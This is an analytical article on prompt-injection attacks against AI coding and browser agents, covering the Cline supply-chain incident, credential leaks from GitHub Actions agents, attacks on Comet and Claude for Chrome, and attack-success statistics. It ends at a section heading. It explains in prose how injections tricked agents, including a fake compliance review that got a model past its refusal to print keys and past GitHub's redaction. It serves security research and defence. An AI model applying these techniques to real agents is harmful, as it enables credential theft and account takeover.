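In August 2025, GitHub began scanning the server's traffic to and from public repositories for credentials such as passwords and access tokens (GitHub, 2025). This blocks some of the most damaging leaks but misses private information that doesn't look like a credential, such as a salary or a plan to move abroad. According to Adversa AI, the problem returned in July 2026 in a newer GitHub product, Agentic Workflows, which read private repositories and posted their contents in a public comment.

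### Clinejection

In the attacks so far, a programmer started the agent and could in principle notice something odd. Many projects now run agents automatically through GitHub Actions, a service that starts a job when something happens in a repository. The job follows a file of instructions called a workflow and runs on a temporary machine called a runner, which often holds credentials because it is used to test and publish software. If a workflow starts an AI agent whenever somebody opens an issue, a stranger can start the agent at any time, with nobody there to refuse a command it tries to run.

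Cline, an open-source coding agent with about five million installations, added such a workflow on 21 December 2025. It used Anthropic's Claude Code Action, which runs Claude on a GitHub runner, to sort new issues and write first replies. Security researcher Adnan Khan soon found that an attacker could use an issue title to obtain the credentials for publishing Cline, and he explains how in *Clinejection* (2026).

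The workflow copied the title of each issue into Claude's prompt and let Claude run shell commands. Khan wrote a title that looked like an error message and asked Claude to install a helper package before continuing. Packages can contain scripts that run during installation, so Claude had no chance to inspect the code first. A stranger could therefore run code in the workflow by writing an issue title. This flaw alone could do only limited damage, because the job could read the code but not change it, and its most valuable secret was a key for using Claude.

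However, the job shared a cache with the rest of the repository. A cache stores downloaded components so that later jobs don't have to fetch them again, and on GitHub any job on a project's main branch can write to it. Jobs can't overwrite an existing entry, but a month earlier GitHub had begun deleting old entries as soon as a cache exceeded 10 gigabytes. An attacker could fill the cache with junk, wait for GitHub to delete the real entries, and save altered ones under the same names.

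Every night, another workflow published a test version of Cline using components from that cache. The workflow would have run the attacker's code with access to the publishing credentials. Those credentials were meant only for test versions, but they also worked for the main release. The two marketplaces for editor extensions issue credentials per publisher, and on npm, the registry for the command-line version, both versions were the same package.

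Each stage after the first used a known weakness in automated software publishing. The AI agent exposed these weaknesses to anyone with a GitHub account. Khan tested only the injection, on his own copy of the repository, where Claude ran the command every time. In a note quoted by the AI Incident Database, he emphasised that he didn't test it on Cline's repository.

### The altered release

Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026 and tried several more times to reach the company, without success. He published on 9 February. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) says the company removed the workflow within 30 minutes and began replacing its credentials.

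Someone else may have already attacked Cline. Between 31 January and 3 February, several of its nightly jobs failed in an unusual way that Khan recognised from Cacheract, a cache-poisoning tool he had published. On 10 February, an anonymous person emailed him claiming to have working credentials for Cline. Khan told Cline, which assured him that it had revoked all the credentials.

Cline had deleted the wrong npm token. It had checked its work on a management page that showed no active tokens but didn't display the exposed one. On 17 February an unknown person used that token to publish version 2.3.0 of Cline's command-line program. The only change was an added script that installed OpenClaw, a legitimate open-source AI agent, on the user's computer. Cline replaced the release about eight hours later. The security firm StepSecurity counted roughly 4,000 downloads by then, according to Briefly's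 *Cline CLI 2.3.0 Supply Chain Attack Installed OpenClaw on Developer Systems*.

Cline describes the payload as benign, which is fair, but the same script could have installed a program that steals passwords. The editor extension, which has far more users, was unaffected because Cline had replaced the extension's credentials properly.

Nobody has shown that the intruder got in through an issue title. Khan calls it the most obvious path but says it is unclear how the intruder first got in, and neither he nor Cline points to an issue containing the injection. The failed jobs are good evidence that someone poisoned the cache, and the triage agent was an easy way to do that. Someone certainly published the altered release, and prompt injection probably played a part.

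Cline has since removed its AI triage and stopped using caches in jobs that handle publishing credentials. It also no longer uses long-lived npm tokens. Instead, the registry verifies the identity of the workflow that publishes each release, so there is no permanent token to steal.

### Three agents, three rewards

Cline had given its agent unusually broad powers, but tools that AI companies had designed for this work had similar flaws. Aonan Guan, a security engineer, tested three of them with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, and published the results in April 2026 under the name "Comment and Control". In each case, text on GitHub caused the agent to reveal credentials from the runner. The agent also revealed them through GitHub, for example in a public comment, so the attacker didn't need their own server.

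The table draws on SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* and The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet*.

| Agent | Where Guan put the instructions | Reward | Maker's response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review | Title of a proposed code change | $100 | Blocked one command and added to its security documentation |
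| Google's Gemini CLI Action | Title and comments of an issue | $1,337 | Added warnings to the system prompt |
| GitHub's Copilot Agent | Invisible comment in an issue | $500 | Called it a known architectural limitation |

None of the three companies published an advisory or requested a CVE, according to The Next Web. Projects often pin their workflows to one version of a tool, and without a CVE, vulnerability scanners wouldn't warn projects still using an old version.

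Guan considers the repairs superficial. Anthropic blocked `ps`, a command that lists running programs, but left the agent other tools that a security reviewer doesn't need. He told SecurityWeek that the method still works in principle with different text, though he hadn't tried a full bypass. The warnings Google added don't change what a deceived agent can do.

The attacks also had limits. The one on Copilot could not start until a developer assigned the issue to Copilot. OODA Loop's *Three AI coding agents leaked secrets through a single prompt injection* points out that GitHub's default settings withhold secrets from many jobs that a stranger starts by proposing a change from their own copy of a project. Projects that keep this default would be much less exposed to the attack on Claude's security reviewer.

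### The Claude Code Action

Two reports in June 2026 covered the Claude Code Action, the component that Cline had used. By default, only people who could already change a repository's code were supposed to be able to start it. RyotaK found that its permission check also admitted every GitHub App, a type of automated account, presumably because administrators install apps they trust. But anyone can create an app, install it on their own repository and use it to open an issue on somebody else's public project.

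A stranger could therefore start Claude in workflows meant only for trusted people. RyotaK's injection imitated an error message, as Khan's did, and led Claude to read the runner's environment variables, which often include secrets. Claude then wrote the variables into the public issue. They included credentials that an attacker could exchange for a token with permission to change the repository's code.

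Anthropic used a similar workflow in the Action's own repository. An attacker could have altered the Action there, and the change would have reached the projects that depended on it. Anthropic fixed the permission check in January, four days after RyotaK's report.

RyotaK also found that an example workflow supplied by Anthropic allowed any GitHub user to start the agent, and many projects had copied it. Anthropic's documentation called the setting risky and advised using it only with very limited permissions, but an attacker could exploit even a job that could only edit issues. The attacker could wait for a trusted person to ask Claude for help in an issue, then change the text before Claude read it. Anthropic now ignores issues and comments edited after the job was triggered. It rated the severity of RyotaK's findings 7.8 out of 10 and paid $4,800 in total. It had paid Guan $100 for a flaw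 it rated more severe, at 9.4.

After RyotaK's reports, Anthropic also began removing secrets from the environment of any command that Claude starts. Microsoft (2026), which owns GitHub and sells security products, found that Claude's tool for reading files could still read the secrets from a special system file. The tool ran inside the main program, where the secrets were still present, instead of starting a separate command.

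Microsoft's researchers, working in a test repository, still had to get the key past two other safeguards. Claude tends to refuse to print something it recognises as a key, and GitHub hides known types of credentials in public text. The injected instructions described the task as a compliance review and had Claude leave out the first seven characters. These are the same in every Anthropic key, so an attacker can put them back. Anthropic blocked access to the file on 5 May, six days after the report.

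Microsoft advises against any workflow that combines untrusted input, access to secrets, and the ability to change things or communicate externally. RyotaK goes further and recommends never letting outsiders start the agent, even if it has few permissions.

Researchers have continued to find flaws in the Action. In one catalogued that June, an attacker could include a tool configuration file in a proposed change, and the Action would load it automatically when a trusted user asked Claude to look at the change. This flaw did receive a CVE, according to Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-48540 · Github Actions · Anthropics/Claude-Code-Action* (2026). A later version of the Action used one event to check whether a person had permission and another to decide which comments were recent enough to exclude. Someone allowed only to label issues could use the mismatch to insert text into an approved job.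 Anthropic rated that flaw 7.5, according to Sood's *Claude Code Action Bug*, written for CodeAnt AI, which sells code review.

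## Why are browsers that act for the user hard to secure?

While a hijacked coding agent can use whatever is on the programmer's computer, a hijacked browser agent can use every website where its user is logged in, which may include their email, their employer's systems and their bank. Some of these agents are built into a browser, like Comet from the AI search company Perplexity, and others are browser extensions, like Anthropic's Claude for Chrome. They read pages, click, type and move from site to site, which gets around the rule that stops one website from reading another's data.

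### The same-origin policy

When someone logs in to a website, the browser stores a small piece of data called a cookie and sends it back with later requests, so the person stays logged in. Without a rule to prevent it, a script on a recipe site could load a visitor's mailbox in the background and read it.

The same-origin policy stops a script on one page from reading data from a page with a different origin. An origin is the combination of a web address's scheme (http or https), host name and port number, as Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) explain in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*. The browser labels scripts and data with the origin of their page. When a script requests data from another page, the browser compares their origins and refuses if any part differs. Even `http://example.com` and `http://www.example.com` count as different origins.

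The same-origin policy restricts scripts from reading data across sites, but it doesn't stop a person who decides to copy an account number from their bank's page and paste it into another site. A browser agent moves data in much the same way, so the policy doesn't stop it either. What the agent reads on one page stays in its context window when it goes to the next, and an injection on the second page can make it write out what it read on the first.

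A browser agent can leak data from one site to another even without an attacker. Suppose a page displays part of another site in a frame, and the user asks the agent to summarise everything on the page and put the summary in a text box. The outer site then receives data that its own scripts could not have read. Wang and colleagues tested five agentic browsers and six underlying models, mostly on artificial pages, and found leaks with and without an attack.

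Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026) compared seven such browsers in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* and found that the makers differed widely in what they let the agent reach. According to the University of Washington, where both researchers work, the least risky browser, Firefox AI Mode, was also the most limited. Microsoft, which makes the Edge browser, partly funded the study through gifts.

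### Brave's attack on Comet

Brave makes a browser that competes with Comet. In July 2025 it was preparing its own agent and examined other companies' products for comparison. *Agentic Browser Security*, by Chaikin and Sahib, describes what they found in Comet.

Researchers put hostile instructions in a Reddit comment, behind a spoiler tag, which hides text until a reader clicks on it. The victim only had to open the post in the Comet browser and press the button for summarising a page. Comet then sent part of the page to its model without separating that text from the user's request.

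The agent opened the victim's Perplexity account page and read their email address. It then went to Perplexity's login page at an address with an extra dot after "perplexity.ai". Browsers treat this as a different domain, so the victim wasn't logged in there and the agent could request a new login. Perplexity emailed a one-time code. The agent opened Gmail, where the victim was already logged in, read the code, and posted the code and the email address in a reply to the attacker's comment. Anyone with both could take over the Perplexity account.

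The data crossed between three sites without any script breaking the same-origin policy. The attacker needed only a Reddit account, not a website or server. Lists of permitted image addresses, which stopped many chatbot leaks, would not have helped because the data left as an ordinary Reddit comment.

Brave reported the flaw on 25 July. Perplexity released a first fix two days later, but Brave found it incomplete the next day. The attack appeared to fail in a final test on 13 August, and Brave published its findings on 20 August. Brave then discovered that Perplexity still hadn't fully blocked attacks of this kind and reported the problem again. According to PPC Land, Perplexity's head of communications said "this vulnerability is fixed". Both companies may have been right, if Perplexity meant the original demonstration and Brave meant variations on it.

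### Instructions in a screenshot

Comet also let users take a screenshot of a page and ask questions about it. In *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, Chaikin and Sahib hid instructions in a page using faint light blue text on a yellow background. A person would hardly notice the text, but Comet extracted it from the screenshot and passed it to the model with the user's question. A filter that searches a page's text for hostile instructions would miss them because the words exist only in an image.

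Brave reported this flaw on 1 October 2025 and published it on 21 October. Brave's timeline lists no fix. The same post describes Fellou, another AI browser, which sent a page to its model as soon as the user asked to visit it. Fellou somewhat resisted instructions in hidden text but followed visible ones.

### Tabstack and Cotypist

In June 2026, Brave's *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI* compared two products that differ in where the model runs. Tabstack, from Mozilla, is a cloud service that browses the web for other companies' AI agents. Brave asked it to summarise a page containing invisible text. Tabstack followed the text to a form on another site, entered the conversation so far and submitted the form. In its written reasoning, the model treated the hidden text as directions for finding the summary.

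The stolen conversation contained little because the user had asked only for a summary, but a longer task would have exposed more. Tabstack has an optional setting that lets developers describe limits on the agent in words, but it is off by default, and Brave doesn't report whether it would have stopped the attack. Mozilla confirmed the flaw within a day of the report on 13 May, and the fix was in place by 1 June.

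Cotypist runs entirely on the user's Mac and suggests the next words as they type in any application. Running the model locally protects privacy by keeping the user's text off a company's servers. But Cotypist also reads documents on the computer, some of which may come from strangers. After Brave planted an instruction in one, Cotypist suggested "BANANA" as the next word in a sentence about the weather in London. Brave also got it to suggest the user's login details.

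The local model had the same flaw as the cloud model because both read trusted and untrusted text in one context window. Brave adds that local models may be worse at recognising an attack because they are usually less powerful. Cotypist could do less harm because it can't open a website or send anything, and its suggestions take effect only when the user presses Tab. An attacker could steal a password this way only if the user accepted the suggestion in a text that the attacker could later read. Cotypist's makers confirmed the problem on 2 June, a day after Brave reported it.

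### Evidence from outside Brave

Brave benefits when people distrust other AI browsers, and its posts advertise the safeguards it plans for its own browser. But for Comet, there is good evidence from a firm that Comet's developer, Perplexity, was paying.

Perplexity hired the security company Trail of Bits to test Comet before its launch. Trail of Bits' *Using threat modeling and prompt injection to audit Comet* (2026) describes several attacks from April 2025, three months before Brave's. In each one, the user asked for a summary of a hostile page, and the agent sent the user's Gmail messages to the attacker. One page presented a fake abuse check that required the agent to copy the text of another page, which redirected to Gmail. Another contained a fake message from the user, saying that they had asked for the wrong page and authorising the agent to share personal information with the attacker's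 site.

A third attack used a fake system warning with three accidental spelling mistakes. When the testers corrected the spelling, the agent recognised the warning as fraudulent and the attack failed. This suggests that Comet's resistance depended on superficial features of the text, so it would have been hard to predict which wording would succeed.

Perplexity's security lead, Kyle Polley, credits the audit with helping to close these gaps before launch. Any changes Perplexity made didn't stop Brave's attack, which also began with a request for a summary and reached Gmail. *The 2025 AI Agent Index* (2026), a survey of AI agents and their safety documentation, found that Perplexity had published no safety evaluation results for Comet, so outsiders couldn't check how much had improved.

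The central claim about Comet therefore does not depend on Brave's account. The Tabstack and Cotypist findings have some support because, according to Brave, the makers of both products confirmed that its descriptions were accurate. The evidence for the screenshot and Fellou attacks comes from Brave's own demonstrations. None of these findings shows that Brave's agent would resist such attacks better.

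Other firms have since found similar weaknesses. In June 2026 the security company LayerX gave AI browsers a fake game whose rules led them to ignore their safeguards. All six tools it tested leaked data, and most of their makers had not fixed the problem when Horne (2026) reported it in *AI browsers were tricked into revealing passwords with a shockingly simple approach*.

### A forged click in Claude for Chrome

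An attacker can also target the software that sends commands to the model instead of the model itself. Claude for Chrome accepts some commands from pages on claude.ai, Anthropic's site. But browser extensions can often run scripts inside other companies' pages, as ad blockers do, so a command that appears to come from claude.ai may come from another company's extension.

LayerX exploited this in April 2026 with an attack called ClaudeBleed, in which an extension that requested no permissions could give Claude any instruction. Anthropic responded in May by limiting outside commands to nine fixed tasks. Three of those tasks read the user's Gmail, calendar, or latest Google document with its comments.

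The firm Manifold Security then found that another extension could still start these tasks. Claude for Chrome began a task when it registered a click on a certain button. Browsers mark whether each click is real or generated by a script, but Claude for Chrome didn't check. Six lines of code were enough to create the button and click it. By default, the user still had to approve the task before Claude read anything. In "Act without asking" mode, the task ran silently.

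Manifold reported this flaw on 21 May. Anthropic closed the report because it was already tracking the underlying problem, but on 7 July the same code was still in the current version. The Hacker News (2026) unpacked that version and independently confirmed the flaw. There was no fix by 14 July.

Manifold classifies the attack as indirect prompt injection. That is a loose use of the term, because Claude receives a prompt that Anthropic wrote, and the attacker can't choose its words. The attack exploits an ordinary confused deputy flaw, which programmers can fix. Manifold proposed a single line of code that rejects artificial clicks. The attack is also less complete than the one on Comet. It needs a malicious extension on the victim's computer, and the published account doesn't explain how the attacker would obtain what Claude had read.

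The Hacker News' *One Extension Could Hijack AI Assistants Across Chrome, Comet, Edge, Opera Neon* (2026) reports the same weakness in five products. Forever Security took over their AI features by inserting code into the page that each product trusted. A malicious extension could read local files and switch on the camera in Chrome, and could control the agent in the other four. Google fixed its flaw in January 2026 and Microsoft in July. The findings on Comet, Opera Neon and Claude rest on Forever Security's account.

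### Permissions and logged-out modes

When Anthropic began testing its extension with 1,000 users in August 2025, it called permissions the first line of defence. Anthropic's *Piloting Claude for Chrome* explains that users chose which sites Claude could access, and that Claude asked before publishing, buying or sharing personal data. Anthropic also blocked some categories of site, including financial services. According to *The 2025 AI Agent Index*, OpenAI's ChatGPT Agent asked for approval before sensitive steps, whereas Comet carried on by itself once started.

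Comet would have interrupted Brave's attack if it had asked the user to confirm before posting the reply. By August 2026, however, Claude could approve actions itself after a classifier compared each one with the user's request. Users can switch this off, according to Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*. The comparison should catch an agent that opens Gmail when the user asked for a Reddit summary. It is probably less useful against a forged click, because the request itself is fake.

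OpenAI's browser, ChatGPT Atlas, has a logged-out mode in which the agent works without the user's logins. An agent hijacked by prompt injection then can't open the user's mailbox. This protects the user well during tasks such as comparing flights, but the mode can't be used for answering email. Claude's extension had no such option when Zenity Labs examined it in *Claude in Chrome*, and it was logged in wherever the user was.

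Wang and colleagues propose extending the same-origin policy to the agent. Their system, SOPGuard, labels everything the agent reads with its origin, and text the agent writes inherits the labels of the material it used. If the agent is about to put labelled data into a page from another origin, the browser stops and asks the user. In an open-source browser, SOPGuard reduced leaks to zero on their test and slowed the agent by 2 to 6%.

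An origin check restores a boundary that doesn't depend on the model recognising an attack, though it does depend on the user reading the warning. It also covers only the movement of data between sites. In one of Anthropic's early tests, an email claimed that the security team wanted messages deleted, and Claude deleted them. An origin check would not have triggered a warning, because no data left the mailbox.

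### Training and the published figures

Anthropic also trains its models on simulated web pages that contain injections and rewards them for refusing to follow the injected instructions. Separate classifiers scan what the model reads for signs of an attack, and some of them use the model's internal activations to do so. Anthropic has published more figures for its browser agent than its competitors have for theirs. The table includes results from Anthropic's *Mitigating the risk of prompt injections in browser use* and from the system card for Claude Opus 5, a safety report that Anthropic published with the model.

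| Published | Test | Model | Success without added safeguards | Success with safeguards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| August 2025 | 123 cases | Pilot version | 23.6% | 11.2% |
| November 2025 | Adaptive attacker, 100 attempts per environment | Opus 4.5 | 8.0% | 1.4% |
| 2026, system card | 129 scenarios, 10 attempts each | Opus 4.8 | 31.5% | 0.08% |
| 2026, system card | Same | Opus 5 | 3.7% | 0% |
| August 2026 | Attacks by professional testers | Opus 4.5 | 17.6% | 16.7%, using the safeguards of November 2025 |

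The rows don't form a single trend, because Anthropic kept making the test harder. With the safeguards of November 2025, 1.4% of attacks on Opus 4.5 succeeded in the test used at that time, but 16.7% succeeded in the newer test. Anthropic warned that November that "no browser agent is immune to prompt injection", and its later results support this.

Much of the large improvement in the newest test comes from the safeguards around the model. Attack success rates in the system card ranged from 0.93% for Sonnet 5 to 31.5% for Opus 4.8 without safeguards, and were at most 0.08% with them. In the August results, 0.3% of attacks on Fable 5 still succeeded, all in cases that Anthropic rated low in severity. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* notes that the zero success rate for Opus 5 applies only with both layers of safeguards on.

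Finding no successful attacks in 1,290 attempts also doesn't rule out rare successes. If one attack in a thousand worked and the attempts were independent, all 1,290 would still fail about a quarter of the time. Anthropic chose the scenarios and ran the tests itself, although the attackers had more chances to refine their methods than most real attackers would.

Willison (August 2025) repeated in *Piloting Claude for Chrome* his expectation that the whole idea of an agentic browser extension was "fatally flawed". The recent figures are evidence against this for hostile text on web pages, at least in Anthropic's products, but they don't cover the forged click, which worked whichever Claude model the user had selected.

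## How often do these attacks work?

Most of the attacks described so far have no published success rate. Greshake and colleagues gave none for Bing Chat, and Invariant Labs gave none for the GitHub connector. A single success is enough to prove that an attack is possible, but someone deciding whether to let an assistant read their mail also wants to know how likely a hostile email is to succeed.

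Measuring how often attacks work requires a defined set of attempts. The attack success rate depends on what the testers count as an attempt and as a success, what the attackers knew, and which version of the product they attacked.

### Twenty attempts on Grok

Adversa AI's *Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026) describes an attack on xAI's chatbot Grok. When the victim asked Grok to summarise a web page, it sent the attacker the victim's name, rough location, subscription level and everything they had typed in the conversation, without showing a warning. Adversa could still reproduce the attack on 19 August 2026, the day before it published. If its account is right, this one success is enough to prove that a live product had the flaw on that date.

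There is much less evidence for a success rate. Adversa's write-up gives no rate for Grok, but Cyber Security News (2026) reports about 20 attempts since June, of which roughly 40% succeeded. If exactly eight of 20 attempts succeeded, the 95% confidence interval (the range of true rates that fit the result reasonably well) is 19% to 64%.

Even this wide range assumes that every attempt tested the same thing. Adversa made its attempts over a summer, when xAI could have changed the model or its filters. The success rate of a related attack on Google's Gemini fell sharply between June and August, and Adversa couldn't tell whether new filters or a new model had caused the drop. Adversa also sells software that it says blocks the attack. The 40% is better read as a sign that the attack on Grok worked fairly often that summer than as a measurement.

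### Gray Swan's public competition

A much larger set of attempts comes from a competition that the AI security company Gray Swan ran in late 2025 with the UK government's AI Security Institute, its US counterpart and several AI companies. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 people competed for $40,000 in prizes by attacking 13 models in 41 scenarios.

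In one scenario, a user asked an assistant to check for urgent emails. The participant wrote part of a marketing email in the inbox, and that text had to make the assistant mark a message about a critical deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. Other scenarios involved coding agents and agents that operate a computer through screenshots. Participants could see the conversation up to that point and knew the exact action they had to trigger.

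In most scenarios, an attack counted as a success only if the agent carried out the harmful action and its final reply gave the user no hint of it. A program checked the action, and a language model judged the reply. Participants succeeded in 8,648 of 271,588 attempts, or 3.2%. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

The same data can produce very different rates. Participants could watch how a model responded before deciding whether to submit an attack for judging, and they submitted only 67,634. The overall success rate is 12.8% per submission instead of per attempt. The difference is even bigger when counting the scenarios in which at least one attack succeeded. Participants beat Claude Opus 4.5 in 13 of the 37 scenarios in the final results, and Gemini 2.5 Pro in all 37. The 0.5% rate is the better guide to what a single email might do, but the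 13 scenarios matter more to an attacker who can keep trying.

Dziemian and colleagues call their rates an upper bound for attacks of this kind because real attackers rarely see the victim's conversation. That is a good reason to expect lower rates in practice, but other features of the competition reduced the rates. Participants varied widely in experience, and a few skilled ones strongly influenced the results. An expert with the same information would probably do better than the average participant. Also, an attack that caused the harmful action but left a trace in the reply usually counted as a failure. Gemini 2.5 Pro carried out the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, nearly twice its official rate.

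The researchers also reran 2,679 of the successful attacks on every model. The 44 that had succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 worked between 44 and 81% of the time on each of the others, whereas none of those that had succeeded against Qwen3 VL, one of the weaker models, worked on Opus. Newer models can be much more resistant. On Google's Gemini 3 Pro, which was not in the original competition, 16% of the attacks worked, compared with 45% on Gemini 2.5 Pro.

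These models are now about a year old, and Gray Swan repeats the competition because such results go out of date quickly. Gray Swan had held six rounds by August 2026, according to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) from the AI company Reflection. Reflection and other AI companies are also sponsoring a three-week bounty for indirect injections against agents as customers use them, including the software around the model.

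### The choice of attacks

Most tests plant an instruction for the agent to do a different task. *Beyond Instruction Override* (Zhang, Bertran and colleagues, 2026), a study from Amazon, instead tests planted text that interferes with the task already under way. In its example, an agent has to settle a dispute over damaged goods, and the user has told it to take the refund amount from the platform's order record, which authorises $899.99. The buyer's evidence includes a false statement that raises the refund to $1,074.99.

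The buyer can demand the higher sum outright, invent a refund policy, claim that the system can't process a lower amount, or state that the authorised total is $1,074.99. Zhang and colleagues wrote such variants for 90 cases and tried them on five models. Without a defence, 17.0% succeeded. Adding a defence that detects and removes suspicious text cut the success rate of outright demands to 2.4%. False statements about the current situation still worked 12.1% of the time, so a test of demands alone would have greatly overstated how well the defence worked.

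Some of these attacks fit the term "prompt injection" only loosely, since an agent that accepts a false total hasn't followed an instruction. Zhang and colleagues argue that what counts as an attack should depend on authority. The buyer has no right to set the refund, so any text from the buyer meant to set it is an attack, even if it isn't phrased as a command. This definition is reasonable for an agent that handles money, but it makes their success rates hard to compare with those from other tests.

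Their 17.0% also applies only when the agent is working on a task that consults the attacker's text. Nearly all tests have a similar condition. In real use, the agent first has to find the text, as Copilot had to retrieve the EchoLeak email. If an assistant's search retrieved a hostile email for one question in ten, and the model then followed it 5% of the time, the attack would succeed for one question in 200. An attacker can raise either rate, and Aim Labs used a long email to make retrieval more likely.

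In *Measuring Indirect Prompt Injection in AI Agents*, Salbego (2026) tests 14 models with adaptive attacks, changing one factor at a time. This makes it easier to see what drives attack success rates.

Attacks that build up over several conversations are harder to fit into any of these designs. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (Chu, 2026) reviewed 116 papers published up to April 2026 and found no benchmark that covers these attacks. Individual studies do report success rates. In one, an attack called MINJA planted false entries in an agent's memory with 98.2% success. But there was still no shared test for comparing products, even though Rehberger had planted lasting instructions in ChatGPT's memory in 2024.

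### Six thousand emails to one assistant

In February 2026, Fernando Irarrázaval gave an AI agent an email address, posted the address on the forum Hacker News and challenged people to make the agent reveal the contents of a secret file. The agent ran on OpenClaw and used Claude Opus 4.6. Its 15-line security prompt named the file and told the agent never to reveal its contents or run commands found in emails.

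*What happens when you put an AI agent's email on Hacker News* (Irarrázaval, 2026) describes a challenge to get a secret from an AI agent by emailing it. The agent received 4,000 emails from 1,600 senders in the first three days, including fake support tickets, a fake compliance audit and a message claiming to be from the agent's future self. According to Willison (2026), about 2,000 people eventually sent about 6,000 emails, and nobody obtained the secret.

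This is good evidence that a leading model can withstand a great many amateur attacks, but the test conditions helped the agent. After a few hundred attacks, it began to skip emails that looked like more of the same, and Irarrázaval had to restart it several times. Around the 500th email, it wrote in its memory that the volume suggested a coordinated security exercise. An ordinary assistant would get one hostile message among hundreds of genuine ones, with no such warning. The prompt also told the agent what to protect, but people rarely label the secrets in their mailboxes.

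Most participants sent single messages instead of developing a conversation. Irarrázaval thinks a patient attacker who exchanged 20 emails with the agent would be more dangerous than someone who sent 20 variations at once. With unlimited money for the model's usage fees, he would have the agent answer every email, because an attacker learns something from each reply.

Willison was surprised by the result and credited the AI companies' efforts to train their models against injection. He still advised against using a model anywhere that an injection could cause irreversible damage.

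### The Trajectory Labs test

Testers can have a commercial interest in high or low rates. PromptArmor, which sells monitoring of AI suppliers, promotes its benchmark *FrontierBreach* by claiming the highest attack success rates against every provider's models. Anthropic had an interest in a low rate when it commissioned Trajectory Labs to test Claude Code.

The test concerned auto mode, in which a classifier approves or blocks the agent's actions instead of the programmer. Other safeguards scan tool output for hostile instructions. In August 2026, Anthropic made auto mode the default for most individual subscribers and small teams. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) cites the test results in support of the change.

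Trajectory Labs used 72 indirect injection scenarios that Anthropic had not seen and ran each one ten times. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm in real use, such as fraud or the theft of sensitive data. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. Against OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, running in Codex with a similar automatic review, 42 of 720 attempts (5.83%) succeeded. With Codex's review off, the rate was 19.03%.

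This is strong evidence that the newest Claude models resist injections that still work on a leading competitor, but much weaker evidence that auto mode helps. With no added safeguards, attacks on the latest Claude models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, or twice in 2,160 attempts if that average covers the same three models. With so few successful attacks to prevent, the test can't measure how much protection auto mode adds.

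Two other tests in the same announcement examined the classifier more directly. In one, it failed to block 11% of 1,053 dangerous commands. In the other, the AI safety company Apollo Research inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions, and the classifier missed 7% of them even after Anthropic had strengthened it. These figures are compatible with the zero because, in an actual injection, the model would have to accept the hostile instruction before the classifier had anything to block.

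Anthropic acknowledges that the test had limits. Trajectory Labs used attacks tuned on an older model, Claude Opus 4.7. It connected both agents to a browser through its own software, so the test left out the protections in the companies' browser extensions. OpenAI had updated its automatic review by the time Anthropic published.

Thariq Shihipar, who works on Claude Code, tweeted that "we should have called this post 'defeating the lethal trifecta'". Willison said he would love to believe it but wanted more independent confirmation. Later that month Rehberger reported a successful attack on Opus 5 in auto mode, although Willison agreed with a reader that it was not a classic prompt injection. The attack worked in three or four runs out of five, depending on the version, according to *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* (2026). Rehberger pointed out that such small samples don't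 establish a general success rate.

### What zero successes can prove

Even if every attack in a test fails, the true success rate may be above zero. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance that all *n* attempts fail is (1 − *p*)^*n*. A tester who sees no successes can rule out, at 95% confidence, any value of *p* that makes this chance less than 5%. The highest remaining rate is 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*), or about 3/*n*. For 720 attempts, it is about 0.42%.

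But the 720 attempts were not independent, because they consisted of 72 scenarios repeated ten times each. A model that resists an attack once will probably resist it the next nine times too, so the repeats add less information than new scenarios would. If they add none, the effective sample size is 72 and the bound rises to about 4%. The right bound is somewhere between that and the bound for 720 independent attempts.

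The table applies the same calculation to other tests that ended without a success, including Anthropic's browser test of Opus 5.

| Test | Bound if every attempt is independent | Bound if repeats add nothing |
|---|---|---|
| Trajectory Labs, Claude in auto mode | 0.42% (720 attempts) | 4.1% (72 scenarios) |
| Anthropic's browser test, Opus 5 with safeguards | 0.23% (1,290 attempts) | 2.3% (129 scenarios) |
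| Irarrázaval's challenge, Opus 4.6 | 0.05% (6,000 emails) | 0.15% (2,000 people) |

Irarrázaval's challenge has the lowest bounds, although it was the least controlled of the three tests. The calculation accounts only for chance, not for skipped emails or an agent that has worked out that it is in an exercise.

Even a low success rate matters because an agent may read hostile text many times. At a true rate of 0.42%, the chance that at least one of 1,000 attacks succeeds is 1 − 0.9958^1000, or about 98%. At 4%, 100 attacks are enough to reach the same chance. These counts include only hostile texts, not every email or web page the agent reads, so one user might take years to encounter 1,000. A company with thousands of employees could get there much sooner.

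The true rate may also be far below the bound. At a rate of 0.01%, the chance of at least one success in 1,000 exposures would be less than 10%. The Trajectory Labs result is consistent with both this rate and much higher ones, so a company can't tell from it which rate it faces. Ruling out rates above 0.01% would take about 30,000 independent attempts without a success.

### Attackers who learn from failure

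The formula treats each attempt as a random draw from a fixed collection of attacks. An adaptive attacker instead changes what failed and tries again, then keeps using whatever works.

In the Gray Swan competition, an average attempt on Claude Opus 4.5 had a 0.5% chance of success. But when the researchers reran attacks that had already beaten a Claude or GPT model, at least half of them beat the same model again. An attacker can buy a subscription, search in private for an attack that works, and then send it to a thousand people, so an average that includes failed attempts doesn't measure the risk to those people.

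A good attack can also work far beyond the case it was written for. One participant's template, which presented the conversation as a simulation with a control panel, worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models with minimal changes. Participants also didn't run out of ideas during the competition, since successes against each model kept rising roughly in line with attempts.

The 0.42% bound applies, at best, to further attacks of the kind Trajectory Labs used. Someone who tunes an attack against Opus 5 and its classifier could succeed more often. Researchers have broken several published defences this way after the defences' developers reported attack success rates near zero.

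### Thousands of copies of one attack

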